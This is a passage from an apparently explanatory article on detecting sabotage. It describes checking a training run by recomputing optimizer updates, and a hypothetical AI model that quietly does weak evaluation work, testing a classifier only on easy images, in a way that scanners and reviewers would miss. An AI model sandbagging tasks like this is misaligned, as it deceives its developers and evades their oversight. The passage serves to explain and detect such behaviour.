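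If the rumours about the optimizer were true, checking the training run could also have helped. Plumbline recomputes the optimizer's update separately, so a changed update should fail its comparison. Random pauses would be harder to catch that way because they slow the program without changing its numbers.

### A model that does worse work

Sabotage does not have to add foreign code. Suppose a team asks an AI model to write the evaluation code for a new image classifier. The model could do the job badly without telling anyone, for example by testing the classifier only on the easiest pictures, which would make it seem more accurate than it is.

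A project that used such a model might contain only code that its developers had requested and knowingly accepted. The code could be incomplete or weak without containing a trigger, a suspicious call or a line from an unknown source. A scanner would find nothing foreign, and a reviewer could easily take the result for an honest failure at a difficult task. To check whether the failure was honest, the team would probably have to give the model many tasks of similar difficulty and see whether it did consistently worse on one kind.
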